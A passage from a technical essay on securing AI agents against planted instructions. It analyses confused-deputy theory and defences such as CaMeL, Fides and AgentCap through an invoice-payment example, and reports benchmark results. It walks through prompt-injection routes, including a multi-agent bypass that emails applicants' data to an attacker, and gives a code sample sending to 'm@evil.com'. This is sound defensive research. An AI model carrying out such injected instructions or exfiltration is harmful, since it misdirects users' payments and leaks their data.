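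The second row shows a gap in rules based on these three properties. The wrong payment requires a stranger's text and permission to pay, but no secret data. An agent that can access only one invoice and a payment tool might satisfy the Rule of Two and still pay the attacker, unless the operator also counts access to the bank account as sensitive.

The third row requires removing every way to send data. Disabling outgoing mail but leaving payments on would not be enough, because a payment to the attacker could carry a few words from a contract in its reference field.

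### Separate sessions for separate servers

Disconnecting the mail server halfway through a task leaves any planted text in the model's context. Parkinson and colleagues therefore propose that a session keep every property it has ever had until the host discards its context. Any sub-agents the session starts would inherit those properties, and the agent couldn't clear them by requesting a new session.

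To pay the invoice under such a rule, the host could use two sessions:

1. The first session can read the mailbox but can't send messages, pay anyone or reach the web. It fills in a form with three fields: the supplier's name, the invoice number and the amount.
2. The host checks the form without using a language model. The name must match a saved payee, the invoice number must have the expected format, and the amount must be a number below the limit.
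3. The host discards the first session's context and starts a second session, which has the payment server and the checked form but has never seen the email.
4. The second session pays the saved account.

The attacker can't use either session to steal the contracts. The first session reads the planted text but can't access the files or send anything out, and the second never receives the text. The attacker's account number can't reach the second session because the form has no field for it. The attacker could still change the amount, within the limit, or choose a different saved payee.

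The separation depends on keeping the form this restrictive. If the form had a "notes" field, the planted text could pass through that field to the session that makes payments, and discarding the first session's context would achieve little.

The split also prevents some useful work. The second session can't check the email if the amount seems wrong, and neither session can write to the supplier with a question. For a new supplier, the form would need an account number field, which makes the wrong payment possible again unless someone confirms the number another way, such as by calling the supplier on a known phone number.

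Zhu and colleagues describe a related design, IsolateGPT, which runs mutually untrusted applications in separate environments and passes messages between them through a trusted hub. According to Shi and colleagues, users of IsolateGPT must confirm potentially dangerous steps, including communication between applications. A job that uses several servers could therefore require many confirmations.

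Evidence about what separation achieves by itself is limited. Shi and colleagues tested a coordinator with six specialist sub-agents, such as one for banking and one for office work. Without Progent, attacks succeeded slightly less often than against single agents, but the system also completed slightly fewer tasks. They suggest that separating the sub-agents caused both effects, though they didn't test this directly.

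Some proposals combine several ways of setting limits. Noyan's *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* outlines a system that caps each role's permissions, uses a classifier to select permissions for the task, and forbids certain combinations. Parkinson and colleagues would also charge an agent for holding more than a small basic set of permissions. The charge would come out of a limited budget and rise as the agent came closer to a forbidden combination. Under the Rule of Two, they would charge a session with one of the three properties 1.5 times the basic rate and a session with two 3 times the basic rate, and a session with two could not add the third, whatever its budget.

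This could encourage an agent to choose less powerful tools and give up permissions it no longer needs. Parkinson and colleagues have not yet shown that models would respond to the prices. An agent influenced by an attacker might ignore them, so a system outside the model would have to enforce the budget and the forbidden combinations.

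## Why capabilities cannot stop every confused deputy

Even if the host chooses references well and the agent holds only those its task requires, a stranger's text can still affect how the agent uses them. In *On Access Control, Capabilities, Their Equivalence, and Confused Deputy Attacks*, Rajani, Garg and Rezk (2016) proved that ordinary programs have the same problem. They gave what they believe is the first formal definition of a program free from confused-deputy attacks, and showed that some programs fail it even under strict capability rules.

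### A small language with two rules

The proofs concern a programming language with little more than numbers, true-or-false values, assignments, `if` and `while`. A program needs a read reference to read a memory location, and the write reference `W(r)` to write to location `r`.

Each location has an owner, which is one of the language's ranked principals. A region is a stretch of the program that runs with one principal's authority, and its code may write to a location only if that principal ranks at or above the location's owner.

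Rajani and colleagues compare two ways to enforce this policy:

- Under access control, code can hold any reference. The system checks the region's rank each time the code writes.
- Under the capability rule, the system checks every value the code computes. If the value is a write reference that the region may not use, the program stops. A region therefore never obtains such a reference.

This capability rule is stricter than the one in many object-capability systems, which don't consult a policy when one program passes a reference to another. It is a simplified version of what Firefox does when objects pass between websites, and it would take a lot of computation because the system has to check every value.

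One line is enough to show the difference:

```
ρ { W(r1) := W(r2) }
```

The region ρ may write to `r1` but not to `r2`, and the line stores a write reference to `r2` in `r1`. Access control allows this because the only write is to `r1`. Under the capability rule, the program stops when it reaches `W(r2)`. Rajani and colleagues prove that access control allows everything the capability rule allows, and this example shows that it allows strictly more. Neither rule lets a region write to a location it has no right to change.

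The result supports Miller and colleagues' argument that access lists and capabilities are not equivalent. The extra freedom is also dangerous, because an attacker can leave a reference in `r1` for a more powerful program to use.

### A definition that compares outcomes

The definition treats a program as having a gap where an attacker can insert any code, which runs with the attacker's authority. It also needs a set S of locations that the attacker wants to change. The program is free from confused-deputy attacks if, whatever code the attacker inserts, at least one of these conditions holds for each location in S when the program finishes:

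1. The attacker has no control over the location. Its final value would have been the same with any other code in the gap.
2. The attacker didn't need the deputy. Some code running alone with the attacker's authority could have left the same value there.

In symbols, let E[a] be the program with attacker code a in the gap, and let F(P, r) be the value in location r after program P finishes. Every run starts from the same memory. The condition is then:

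```
for all a, and all r in S:
      (for all b:   F(E[b], r) = F(E[a], r))
  or  (for some b:  F(b, r)    = F(E[a], r))
```

Gallo's definition depends on tracing an action back to a request, whereas this one compares only final values. It doesn't cover runs that don't finish, so an attacker who only causes the program to stop has not violated the definition.

### Handing the deputy a reference

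The paper's simplified version of Hardy's compiler works like this:

```
attacker { ... }
compiler { (the location referred to in o) := compile(source code in s) }
```

The attacker's code runs first, with the lowest authority. It puts source code in `s` and a write reference in `o`. The compiler, with the highest authority, then writes its output through that reference.

Suppose the attacker puts a write reference to the billing records in `o`. Access control allows every step, because the attacker may write to `o` and the compiler may write to the billing records. The compiler then overwrites the records with the attacker's compiled code, which the attacker could not have done alone. The attack works even without ambient authority, because the compiler uses a specific reference for this write.

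Under the capability rule, the program stops when the attacker tries to compute the reference. The attacker can pass on only references it could have used directly, so condition 2 holds for any location the compiler writes to. In this kind of attack, which Rajani and colleagues call explicit designation, the deputy gets the write reference from the attacker.

### Influencing a reference the deputy already has

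Their counterexample is even simpler:

```
attacker { ... }
deputy   { W(r) := contents of m }
```

The attacker may write to `m` but not to `r`. Suppose `r` contains 0 at the start. The attack then goes as follows:

1. The attacker writes 42 to `m`, as both rules allow.
2. The deputy reads 42. This is a number and not a reference, so the capability rule doesn't restrict it.
3. The deputy writes 42 to `r` through its own reference, which it has every right to hold.

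If the attacker had written 41, `r` would contain 41, so condition 1 fails. Condition 2 fails because no code with the attacker's authority can write to `r`. The attack therefore succeeds under the capability rule, although the attacker never gave the deputy a reference. Rajani and colleagues compare this attack to SQL injection through a web server that can write to a protected database.

In implicit designation, the deputy already has the reference, in its code or in memory, and the attacker influences what it writes. The attacker doesn't have to supply the value being written. For example, the deputy may read a true-or-false value that the attacker controls, and write 41 if it is true and 42 if it is false.

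These examples concern what the deputy writes, but the definition also covers where it writes. Suppose the deputy has write references to two protected locations, both containing 0, and uses a true-or-false value from the attacker to choose which one to set to 1. The attacker can write to neither location, but the final value of each depends on the attacker's input, so both conditions fail.

Karp (2026), in *Confused deputy*, asked a mailing list whether anyone had proved that a capability system can't contain a confused-deputy vulnerability. Leslie replied that it can, giving a similar case in which a deputy puts its capabilities in a table and lets a client choose one.

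### When capabilities are enough

Rajani and colleagues also prove that the capability rule stops every attack if the program meets two restrictions. Call a location protected if it is in S and the attacker can't write to it. Then:

- the deputy's code must not contain a write reference to any protected location;
- memory must not contain one when the program starts.

The capability rule prevents the attacker from supplying such a reference, so the deputy cannot get one. The deputy never writes to a protected location, and condition 1 holds for every such location.

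These restrictions make the deputy safe by preventing it from changing anything the attacker wants changed. Under them, a compiler couldn't keep its own billing records and a payment agent couldn't make payments. Rajani and colleagues conclude that the restrictions "render the language useless for almost all practical purposes".

Programmers can make an exception by marking a region of code as endorsed, meaning that it acts on an outsider's input on purpose. For example, customers legitimately affect their bills, since the charge can depend on the size of the source file. Neither the restrictions on code nor the definition applies to endorsed regions, so an endorsed region that let customers type in their own bill would not count as a failure.

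### Tracking who influenced a value

Their alternative, which they call provenance tracking, records where values came from. It starts from the access-control rule and labels each value with the least trusted source that contributed to it. A number in the deputy's own code gets the highest label, and a number read from `m` gets the attacker's label. Before a write, the system compares the labels on both the value and the reference with the location's owner, and it refuses the write if either label is too low.

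This stops the counterexample because 42 came from `m`. It also stops the attack on the compiler, because the reference came from `o`.

It doesn't stop the example with the true-or-false value, because both 41 and 42 come from the deputy's own code. Full provenance tracking therefore adds a label for the program's current position. When the deputy enters an `if` that depends on the attacker's data, this label drops to the attacker's level, and the system refuses writes to protected locations until the `if` ends.

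Rajani and colleagues prove that, with this addition, no confused-deputy attack is possible outside endorsed regions, whatever references the deputy holds. Their proof compares two runs that differ only in the attacker's code. Any value that differs between the runs has a low label, and so does any branch that depends on such a value. The system prevents these values and branches from affecting protected locations, so those locations end up the same in both runs, as condition 1 requires.

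The cost is that the system also stops some harmless programs:

| Program | Access control | Capability rule | Labels on values | Full provenance |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Attacker gives the compiler a reference | Attack succeeds | Stopped | Stopped | Stopped |
| Deputy copies the attacker's number | Attack succeeds | Attack succeeds | Stopped | Stopped |
| Attacker's true-or-false value selects the deputy's number | Attack succeeds | Attack succeeds | Attack succeeds | Stopped |
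| No attacker, but a branch depends on less trusted data | Runs | Runs | Runs | Stopped |

*Full Provenance on the COSS Causal Axis* (2026) uses this result to separate the attacks that capability checks prevent from those they don't. *Type-Confusion Security* (2026) proves a similar guarantee for programs that pass a type check, but defines the attack as a call to a trusted function from a context less trusted than the function permits.

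### The invoice agent as the deputy

Rajani and colleagues did not study language models, so applying their result to agents is an inference. In the invoice example, the email takes the place of the attacker's code, and the host and model together are the deputy. The protected location is the record of payments from the user's account.

The agent legitimately holds one reference for reading the email and another for making payments. If text planted in the email influences how the agent uses the payment reference, that is implicit designation. The sender supplies no reference and the agent pays with the one it already holds, so a capability check would allow the call.

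A general payment reference takes the account number as a value, like the 42 in the counterexample, so an agent that copies the attacker's account number from the email into a payment call pays the attacker. The reference `payNorthgate` prevents this because its payee is fixed. The attacker would have to give the agent a reference for paying the attacker from the user's account, and the attacker doesn't have one. Capabilities can therefore stop this attack if each payee has a separate reference.

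The email can still affect whether the agent pays and how much, up to the £500 limit. By the formal definition this is a confused-deputy attack, because the outcome depends on a sender who couldn't have made the payment. The definition also counts an honest invoice as an attack, for the same reason. The host could treat reading the amount as an endorsed step, but the definition would then provide no assurance about that step.

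The definition fits agents imperfectly in other ways too. It compares exact outcomes, but a model may respond differently to the same email on two runs, so a version for agents would probably have to compare probabilities. The definition also covers changes to data but not leaks. If the agent emails the contracts to the attacker, they arrive in a mailbox where the attacker could have written the same text. Condition 2 therefore holds for that mailbox, and the theft doesn't count as an attack on it.

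### The advocates' reply

Capability advocates had already conceded part of this in 2003, when Miller and colleagues wrote that no security model can prevent people from writing bad programs. They claimed only that systems in which a resource's name and the permission to use it are inseparable rule out a common type of confused deputy, in which a malicious party names a resource it shouldn't access. Rajani and colleagues read a diagram in the same paper as suggesting that such systems rule out all confused deputies, but the surrounding text is limited to the narrower claim.

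Some of the disagreement is over what "confused deputy" means. In *Gemini discusses Confused Deputy*, a discussion started by Miller (2026), Karp defines a confused deputy as one that uses its permissions on a resource that someone else designated. By that definition, the program that copies 42 into `r` isn't a confused deputy, because its own code specifies `r`, but the attacker has still changed protected data.

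In the thread that Karp started, Miller says that a deputy is not vulnerable if it uses only capabilities to designate things. He calls this a severe restriction that many normal deputies won't meet, but expects most of them to be safe anyway. His rule of thumb is that a deputy is probably safe if it doesn't use rights amplification, combining references to get more authority than they give separately.

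That may be a good guide for conventional code, where programmers decide which inputs can affect which actions. It is a weaker guide for a language model, because any text in its context might affect any call it proposes. The invoice agent with a general payment reference can pay the attacker without rights amplification.

The advocates have a better argument in the limits that references put on the damage. An attacker who relies on implicit designation can use only the references the deputy already holds. The formal definition doesn't reflect this, because it treats a £20 overpayment and an emptied account alike as failures. For the £480 invoice, narrower references leave the email less to influence:

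| Payment references the agent holds | What the email can influence | Worst result |
| --- | --- | --- |
| A general payment reference | Payee and amount | The whole balance goes to the attacker |
| One for each saved payee, each good for one payment of up to £500 | Which payees get money, and how much | Every saved payee gets £500 |
| `payNorthgate`, for one payment of up to £500 | The amount, and whether to pay | Northgate Paper gets £20 too much, or nothing |
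| One that pays Northgate Paper exactly £480, once | Whether to pay | The bill stays unpaid |

Even the last arrangement fails the formal definition, because the email can still determine whether the payment happens. Few users would mind this as much as losing the whole balance.

Karp says that giving a program only the privileges it needs solves other problems and has nothing to do with confused deputies. He is right that least privilege doesn't remove the confusion, since Hardy's compiler could have destroyed its statistics file even with a license that covered only that file. But least privilege does reduce the damage the confusion can do.

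How far a host can narrow the references depends on the information it has before the agent reads the email. The agent has to pass a new supplier's account number to the payment call as a value, and a capability check can't establish whether that value came from the supplier or an impostor.

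## Checking where the contents of a tool call came from

A host can record the sources of each value and check them before a call runs. This is harder for an agent than for programs in Rajani and colleagues' small language, where it is always clear which values a result depends on. Any word in a language model's context may have affected any argument it writes, so a strict tracker has to treat everything the model writes after reading a stranger's email as coming partly from the stranger. Under that rule, the invoice agent couldn't pay anyone once it had read the invoice. Several designs avoid this problem by controlling what the model has read when it chooses a call.

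### A program written before the agent reads any email

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind published in March 2025, divides the work between two models. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it handles a request:

1. A privileged model reads the user's request and writes a short program in a restricted form of Python. It has seen no outside text.
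2. An interpreter, which is conventional software, runs the program and makes the tool calls. It puts the results in the program's variables and doesn't show them to the privileged model.
3. When the program needs something from free text, it calls a quarantined model. This model has no tools and can only return data, such as an amount.
4. The interpreter tags every value with its sources and its permitted readers, and carries the tags over to anything the program computes from that value.
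5. Before each tool call, a policy examines the tool, the arguments and their tags, then allows or denies the call. One policy, for example, denies a password change unless the new password came from the user.

For the invoice, the program might be:

```
emails  = search_mail(sender="Northgate Paper")
invoice = quarantined_model("Extract the account and amount", emails)
create_payment(account=invoice.account, amount=invoice.amount)
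```

The attacker fails to steal the contracts because no line of this program opens the contracts folder, and the model that could add such a line never receives the planted text.

An attacker can cause a wrong payment without adding a line to the program. The quarantined model reads the email and may return the attacker's account number, which the program then pays. Separating the two models, as Willison proposed in 2023, doesn't prevent this. The tags can, because they record the email as the source of `invoice.account`, and a policy that requires payees to come from the user or the saved payees would then block the payment.

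CaMeL calls these tags "capabilities", but they aren't capabilities in Hardy's sense. A tag describes a value and gives nobody permission to do anything.

### Attacks stopped and tasks lost

*SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a competing system, ran CaMeL's released code on the AgentDojo benchmark. None of 629 attacks succeeded, but without an attack CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks, while SecureClaw completed 59. Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL with Claude Haiku 4.5, and it completed 49 of the 97. Different models and adapter code may explain the difference between the two CaMeL results, so neither is a fixed property of the design.

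Some of the loss comes from CaMeL's policies. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that switching them on halves task completion in AgentDojo's banking tests. The rest comes from planning in advance. The privileged model has to write code that handles a tool's output before seeing any of it, and it can't easily change course when the output is unexpected. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira and Iqbal, 2026) cites a benchmark of open-ended tasks on which CaMeL completed none. *ToolFence* (2026) also found CaMeL much slower than defences that only filter text.

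Planning in advance hurts stronger models less. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested five models on a benchmark where a main agent delegates to four specialists. CaMeL lowered task completion by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. The tests ran CaMeL without any policies, so these losses come from the planning alone.

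### Checking the program before it runs

Nikolaou and colleagues' extension, CaMeLoT, looks for violations before the agent makes any calls. It turns the program into a map of every path execution could take and marks the variables that would hold outside data. Software called a model checker then searches all the paths for one that breaks a rule. If it finds one, the privileged model receives a description of that path and rewrites the program.

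One of CaMeLoT's example rules is that a payment's recipient and amount must both be free of outside influence. The invoice program breaks this rule, so CaMeLoT would reject it before the agent had opened the mailbox. The model could fix part of the problem by getting the recipient from Northgate Paper's entry in the saved payees. But the amount is only in the email, so the rule would block payment of any bill whose total the user hadn't stated.

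CaMeLoT can also enforce rules about the order of steps, which CaMeL's policies can't naturally express because they check one call at a time. In a test scenario about a company's security team, one rule required the agent to get human approval before disconnecting a computer. CaMeLoT caught all seven unsafe programs, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The researchers had chosen the rules to go beyond CaMeL, so the score mainly confirms that the checker works as designed.

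Some facts aren't known before a program runs, such as who will be able to read a shared file when the program reaches it. CaMeLoT fully reproduced 22 of 28 CaMeL policies and left the others to checks at run time. When it can't determine whether a value will be trustworthy, it treats the value as untrustworthy, which sometimes blocks a safe program.

### Places where the tags get lost

Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's tags miss some of the ways in which one value can depend on another. Their example is a version of an old puzzle in computer security, which in simplified form goes like this:

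```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and the program skips the assignment in the fourth line, so `rich` stays true. CaMeL marks a variable as secret only when an assignment runs, so it hasn't marked `rich`, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and the program sends no email. The recipient can therefore tell whether the balance is high or low by whether the email arrives.

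A stranger's email can't insert these lines, because the model that writes the program doesn't read the email. The example matters more as a warning about relying on hand-built interpreters to track where data came from, since CaMeL has no proof that its tags are complete. Garby and colleagues designed a language for agents that does have such a proof, checked by computer. An agent they built in it completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL does without policies, and resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs.

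Peters-Gill and colleagues found a more practical gap, which appears when one CaMeL agent calls another. They asked a main agent to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. It had a database agent and a messaging agent to help, and the database contained a planted request to email the data to an outside address. The attack then went as follows:

1. The database agent returned the records, including the planted text. Its interpreter treated them as untrusted.
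2. The main agent's program had the quarantined model summarize the records, and put the summary into a sentence asking the messaging agent to send it to Julie.
3. The messaging agent treated that whole sentence as its user's request, so its privileged model read the planted text and wrote a program that also emailed the applicants' data to the attacker.

Each agent followed CaMeL's design, but the tags on a tracked value disappeared when the value became part of an ordinary sentence. The remedy is to give agents separate channels for instructions and data, with the data hidden from the receiving agent's privileged model. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output, and the tags travel with the data.

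The researchers then ran 949 attacks against each of five models, on a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents:

| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | CaMeL with two channels |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% succeeded | 0.5% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% | 0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% | 0% |

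GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without CaMeL, so this benchmark can't show what CaMeL would add. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against taking this to mean the model is immune, because attacks that adapt to the model have succeeded in large-scale testing against every leading model tried. The case for using CaMeL with such models therefore rests more on its design than on these scores. With no policies switched on, that design guarantees only that outside text can't add steps to the program, so it would still allow the wrong payment.

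### Two labels on every value

Fides, a system from Microsoft, lets the planning model keep working one step at a time. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give each value one label for whether it is trusted and another for whether it is secret. When the agent combines values, the result is untrusted if any part was untrusted, and secret if any part was secret. In the invoice example, the labels could be:

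| Value | Trusted? | Secret? |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The user's request | Yes | No |
| The saved payees | Yes | Yes |
| The supplier's email | No | Yes |
| A note comparing the email with the saved payees | No | Yes |

A policy can then allow payments only when both the choice of call and its arguments are trusted, and allow messages only to people who may read everything in them. To support the second rule, the secrecy label can list who may read the data. If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a text that draws on both.

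If the model read an untrusted email, all its later calls would count as untrusted. Fides therefore puts untrusted text in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. If a user asks it to forward three emails to a colleague on Slack, the model can write a call that names the colleague and passes the variable as the message. The model chose the recipient without reading the emails, so a policy can allow the call even though the message is untrusted.

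Some tasks depend on what the text contains. If the user wants a calendar entry for any meeting request in the mailbox, the planning model's next step depends on whether the mailbox contains such a request. Fides can send the emails to a quarantined model that may answer only yes or no, and a policy may pass that answer to the planning model, since a yes or no can't carry planted instructions. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model extracts the date and time into another variable, which goes straight to the calendar.

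Costa and colleagues tested Fides on AgentDojo with GPT-4o:

| Agent | Successful attacks | Office tasks done | Travel | Banking | Slack |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Ordinary agent | 152 | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent with labels and policies | 0 | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| Fides without policies | 21 | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| Fides with policies | 0 | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

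The policies stop the attacks, and hiding text in variables lets the agent complete some tasks that the policies would otherwise block. GPT-4o often confused the variables. The later o1 did better, and with it Fides completed 68% of the travel tasks. Both models are old by late 2026, so the task figures probably understate what the design can do now.

The attack counts exclude cases that the researchers read and judged harmless, because AgentDojo's automatic scoring sometimes counts harmless text as an attack. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* reports one such case, in which the agent booked the right hotel but quoted a review recommending the attacker's hotel.

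The labels also had an advantage they wouldn't have in ordinary use, because the researchers marked a field as untrusted if any of AgentDojo's attacks used it. A company labelling its own data doesn't have a list of the fields attackers will use.

Many of the banking failures were intentional. In these tasks, which are much like paying an invoice, the user had asked the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, such as scheduling a payment. The policy blocked these actions because their details came from the file.

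### Coarser labels

Labelling every field is a lot of work, so some systems label larger units. Ntousakis proposes SAMOS, a gateway for MCP that labels whole tools by whether they read or write confidential data. In the GitHub attack, the session becomes "public" when the agent reads the public issue, and the gateway then refuses its request for a private repository. But GitHub's tool for reading files works on both public and private repositories, so someone would have to split it in two or have it report which kind it had opened. The gateway would also block a user's legitimate request to fix a public bug using private notes.

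*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that instead records each event (a message, tool call or result) and which earlier events could have influenced it. An operator can then write a rule that blocks any outgoing message influenced by both untrusted text and secret data. This rule would stop the theft of the contracts, but the operator would need another to stop the wrong payment. On AgentDojo, the system was about as secure as label-based control and completed substantially more tasks.

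### AgentCap's permits and its check on arguments

*AgentCap*, by Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, combines a provenance check with short-lived permits. The model works in the usual way, reading emails and proposing calls, and has to state a purpose for each call. A policy engine outside the model then issues a signed token only if all of these are true:

- The policy lists the tool, and allows it for the stated purpose.
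- Each sensitive argument, such as the recipient of a payment, has support from a trusted source.
- The agent already holds tokens for any steps the policy requires first, such as checking the balance.
- The new token wouldn't complete a forbidden combination with tokens the agent holds in this session.
- The agent's trust score is high enough, and the engine hasn't locked the agent out.

A gateway checks the token's signature, expiry time and number of calls left before it forwards the call. In the banking policy, a token for sending money lasts 30 seconds and works once. The gateway also checks which agent is presenting the token, whereas a macaroon works for anyone who holds it.

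The stated purpose adds little against an attacker, since a misled model will enter "paying a bill" as the purpose. The trust score helps against repeated attempts. It starts at 0.8 and falls by 30% after each refused or abnormal call, so with the default settings the agent loses its permission to change anything after two such calls and all its permissions after three. But an attacker could use this to shut the agent down, by planting text that prompts it to make calls the engine will refuse.

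The operator prevents forbidden combinations by putting permissions into groups that no session may hold together. A separate program checks these rules for mistakes before anyone uses them. In a customer-service policy, it found that no agent could delete a customer record, because the permission required a step that another rule excluded.

The check on arguments works by keeping track of which values each source has made available. Suppose the model proposes a payment to an account. The engine refuses if the account number has appeared only in untrusted text, and accepts if the number is also in the user's request or in a field that the policy trusts. The paper reports these results:

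| Test | Attacks that succeeded, without and with AgentCap | User tasks completed under attack, without and with AgentCap |
| --- | --- | --- |
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% → 5.09% | 73.61% → 74.88% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% → 0% | 75.68% → 75.04% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% → 8.63% | 74.10% → 62.24% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% → 0% | 72.96% → 65.37% |

Without an attack, AgentCap lowered task completion on AgentDojo by 3.1 percentage points with GPT-4o (three of 97 tasks) and 7.2 points with GPT-5.4 (seven tasks). InjecAgent, another benchmark of planted instructions, has 1,054 attacks but only 51 harmless tests. On those 51, AgentCap lowered completion by 11.7 points with GPT-4o and 5.9 points with GPT-5.4.

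The paper also reports results on the same AgentDojo tests for Progent, which writes a policy for each task. With GPT-4o, Progent let more attacks through than AgentCap and completed fewer tasks, at 68.04% versus 78.35% without an attack and 59.64% versus 74.88% under attack. Progent's policies often allowed only the values a model had predicted from the request, whereas AgentCap accepts any value with trusted support.

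The attacks that still worked on GPT-4o fell into three groups. Some aimed only to change what the agent told the user, which involves no tool call for AgentCap to check. In others, the attacker chose an argument that the policy didn't list as sensitive. The rest used a sensitive argument whose value had arrived through a field nobody had marked as untrusted. The last two groups succeeded because of errors in the policy, which a company writing its own could easily make too.

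The comparison with Progent is less even than it looks. The researchers wrote AgentCap's AgentDojo policies before running the tests, but they used the benchmark's own tools and task descriptions, so they knew every task the agent would face, which a real operator would not. They also ran each test only once, so a difference of three tasks could be chance. GPT-5.4 ran with its reasoning switched off, which may have made it easier to mislead than in normal use.

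### The account number that exists only in the email

Suppose the host uses a check like AgentCap's for the invoice. The user's request and the saved payees count as trusted, and the text of emails doesn't. The result depends on where else the account number appears:

| Account number in the proposed payment | Where it appears | Result |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Northgate Paper's usual account | The email and the saved payees | Allowed |
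| The attacker's account | The email only | Refused |
| A new supplier's real account | The email only | Refused |
| Northgate Paper's real new account, after it changes banks | The email only | Refused |

The check stops the wrong payment without stopping the ordinary one. But the last three rows have the same provenance, so no rule based on provenance alone can allow the legitimate payments and refuse the attacker's. Better tracking wouldn't help, because the records are already accurate and all three numbers came only from an email.

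The amount also appears only in the email. Unless the user types the total, the policy has to leave the amount off its list of sensitive arguments and rely on a fixed limit such as £500.

If the planted text names another saved payee, perhaps a dishonest supplier who wants to be paid twice, AgentCap's value matching would accept that supplier's account number because it has trusted support. CaMeL instead follows the path a value took, so a number that the quarantined model extracted from the email keeps the email as its source even if it matches a saved payee. CaMeL could therefore refuse this payment, but it would also refuse to pay Northgate Paper's usual account if the program had copied the number from the invoice instead of looking it up.

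### Who may endorse an account number

To pay a new supplier, someone has to endorse, or mark as trusted, an account number that came from an untrusted email. In Garby and colleagues' language, endorsement is an explicit command, so a reviewer can find every place where a program uses it. The command changes only whether a value is trusted, so a secret account number stays secret. The language does not specify who should be allowed to give the command.

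The agent's own model is a poor choice for this check because the email may already have misled it. Asking a quarantined model whether the email looks genuine is no better, since its answer depends on the same text. Fides's exception for yes-or-no answers doesn't help either. A one-bit answer can't contain an account number, but if a yes to "Is this invoice genuine?" releases the payment, the attacker only has to get the model to answer yes.

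Sequeira and Iqbal's system learns from past runs where each argument normally comes from, then compares sensitive values with a list of known ones. If these checks can't settle a case, a model decides by comparing the proposed call with the user's request. On AgentDojo and a second benchmark, the system blocked 94.3% of attacks that would otherwise have succeeded and allowed about 95% of legitimate runs. The request gives the model strong evidence against a payment when the user asked only for a summary, but much weaker evidence when the user did ask to pay a bill and only the account number is wrong.

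Costa and colleagues point out that mail servers can authenticate a sender's address, so a host could treat the address as trusted even if it distrusts the text. This would expose an email with a forged address at Northgate Paper's domain, but not one sent from a similar-looking domain or from the supplier's real mailbox after someone had broken into it.

The user can endorse the account number, and provenance makes the approval request more useful than a generic prompt. The host could ask only when no trusted source supports a value, which for most people would happen a few times a year, and could give the reason, such as "This account number appears only in an email that arrived today." The user still has to confirm the number outside the email, because rereading it provides no new evidence.

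A business can give the job to whoever keeps its list of verified suppliers. *ActWithin* (2026) describes this for batches of payments. The payer, or a service the payer trusts, signs a list that fixes each payment's recipient, amount, currency and reference. The list can include approved replacements, for instance from a directory of verified recipients, and a limit on how many the agent may use. The agent can suggest entries, but the trusted service decides what goes in. Once the list is signed, the agent can make the payments without further approval, and a separate program rejects any payment that isn't on the list. The paper treats turning a request in ordinary language into such a list as a separate step that nobody has yet validated.

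With a directory, a person has to verify each supplier once, and again whenever its bank details change. As with ScopeGate's list of approved accounts, the agent must not be able to edit the directory based on an email. Provenance records could flag an account saved that way only if they persisted across sessions, and *AgentCap* leaves tracking across sessions and stored memory to future work. Until a host can store each value together with its sources, it is safer to let the agent read the directory but not change it.
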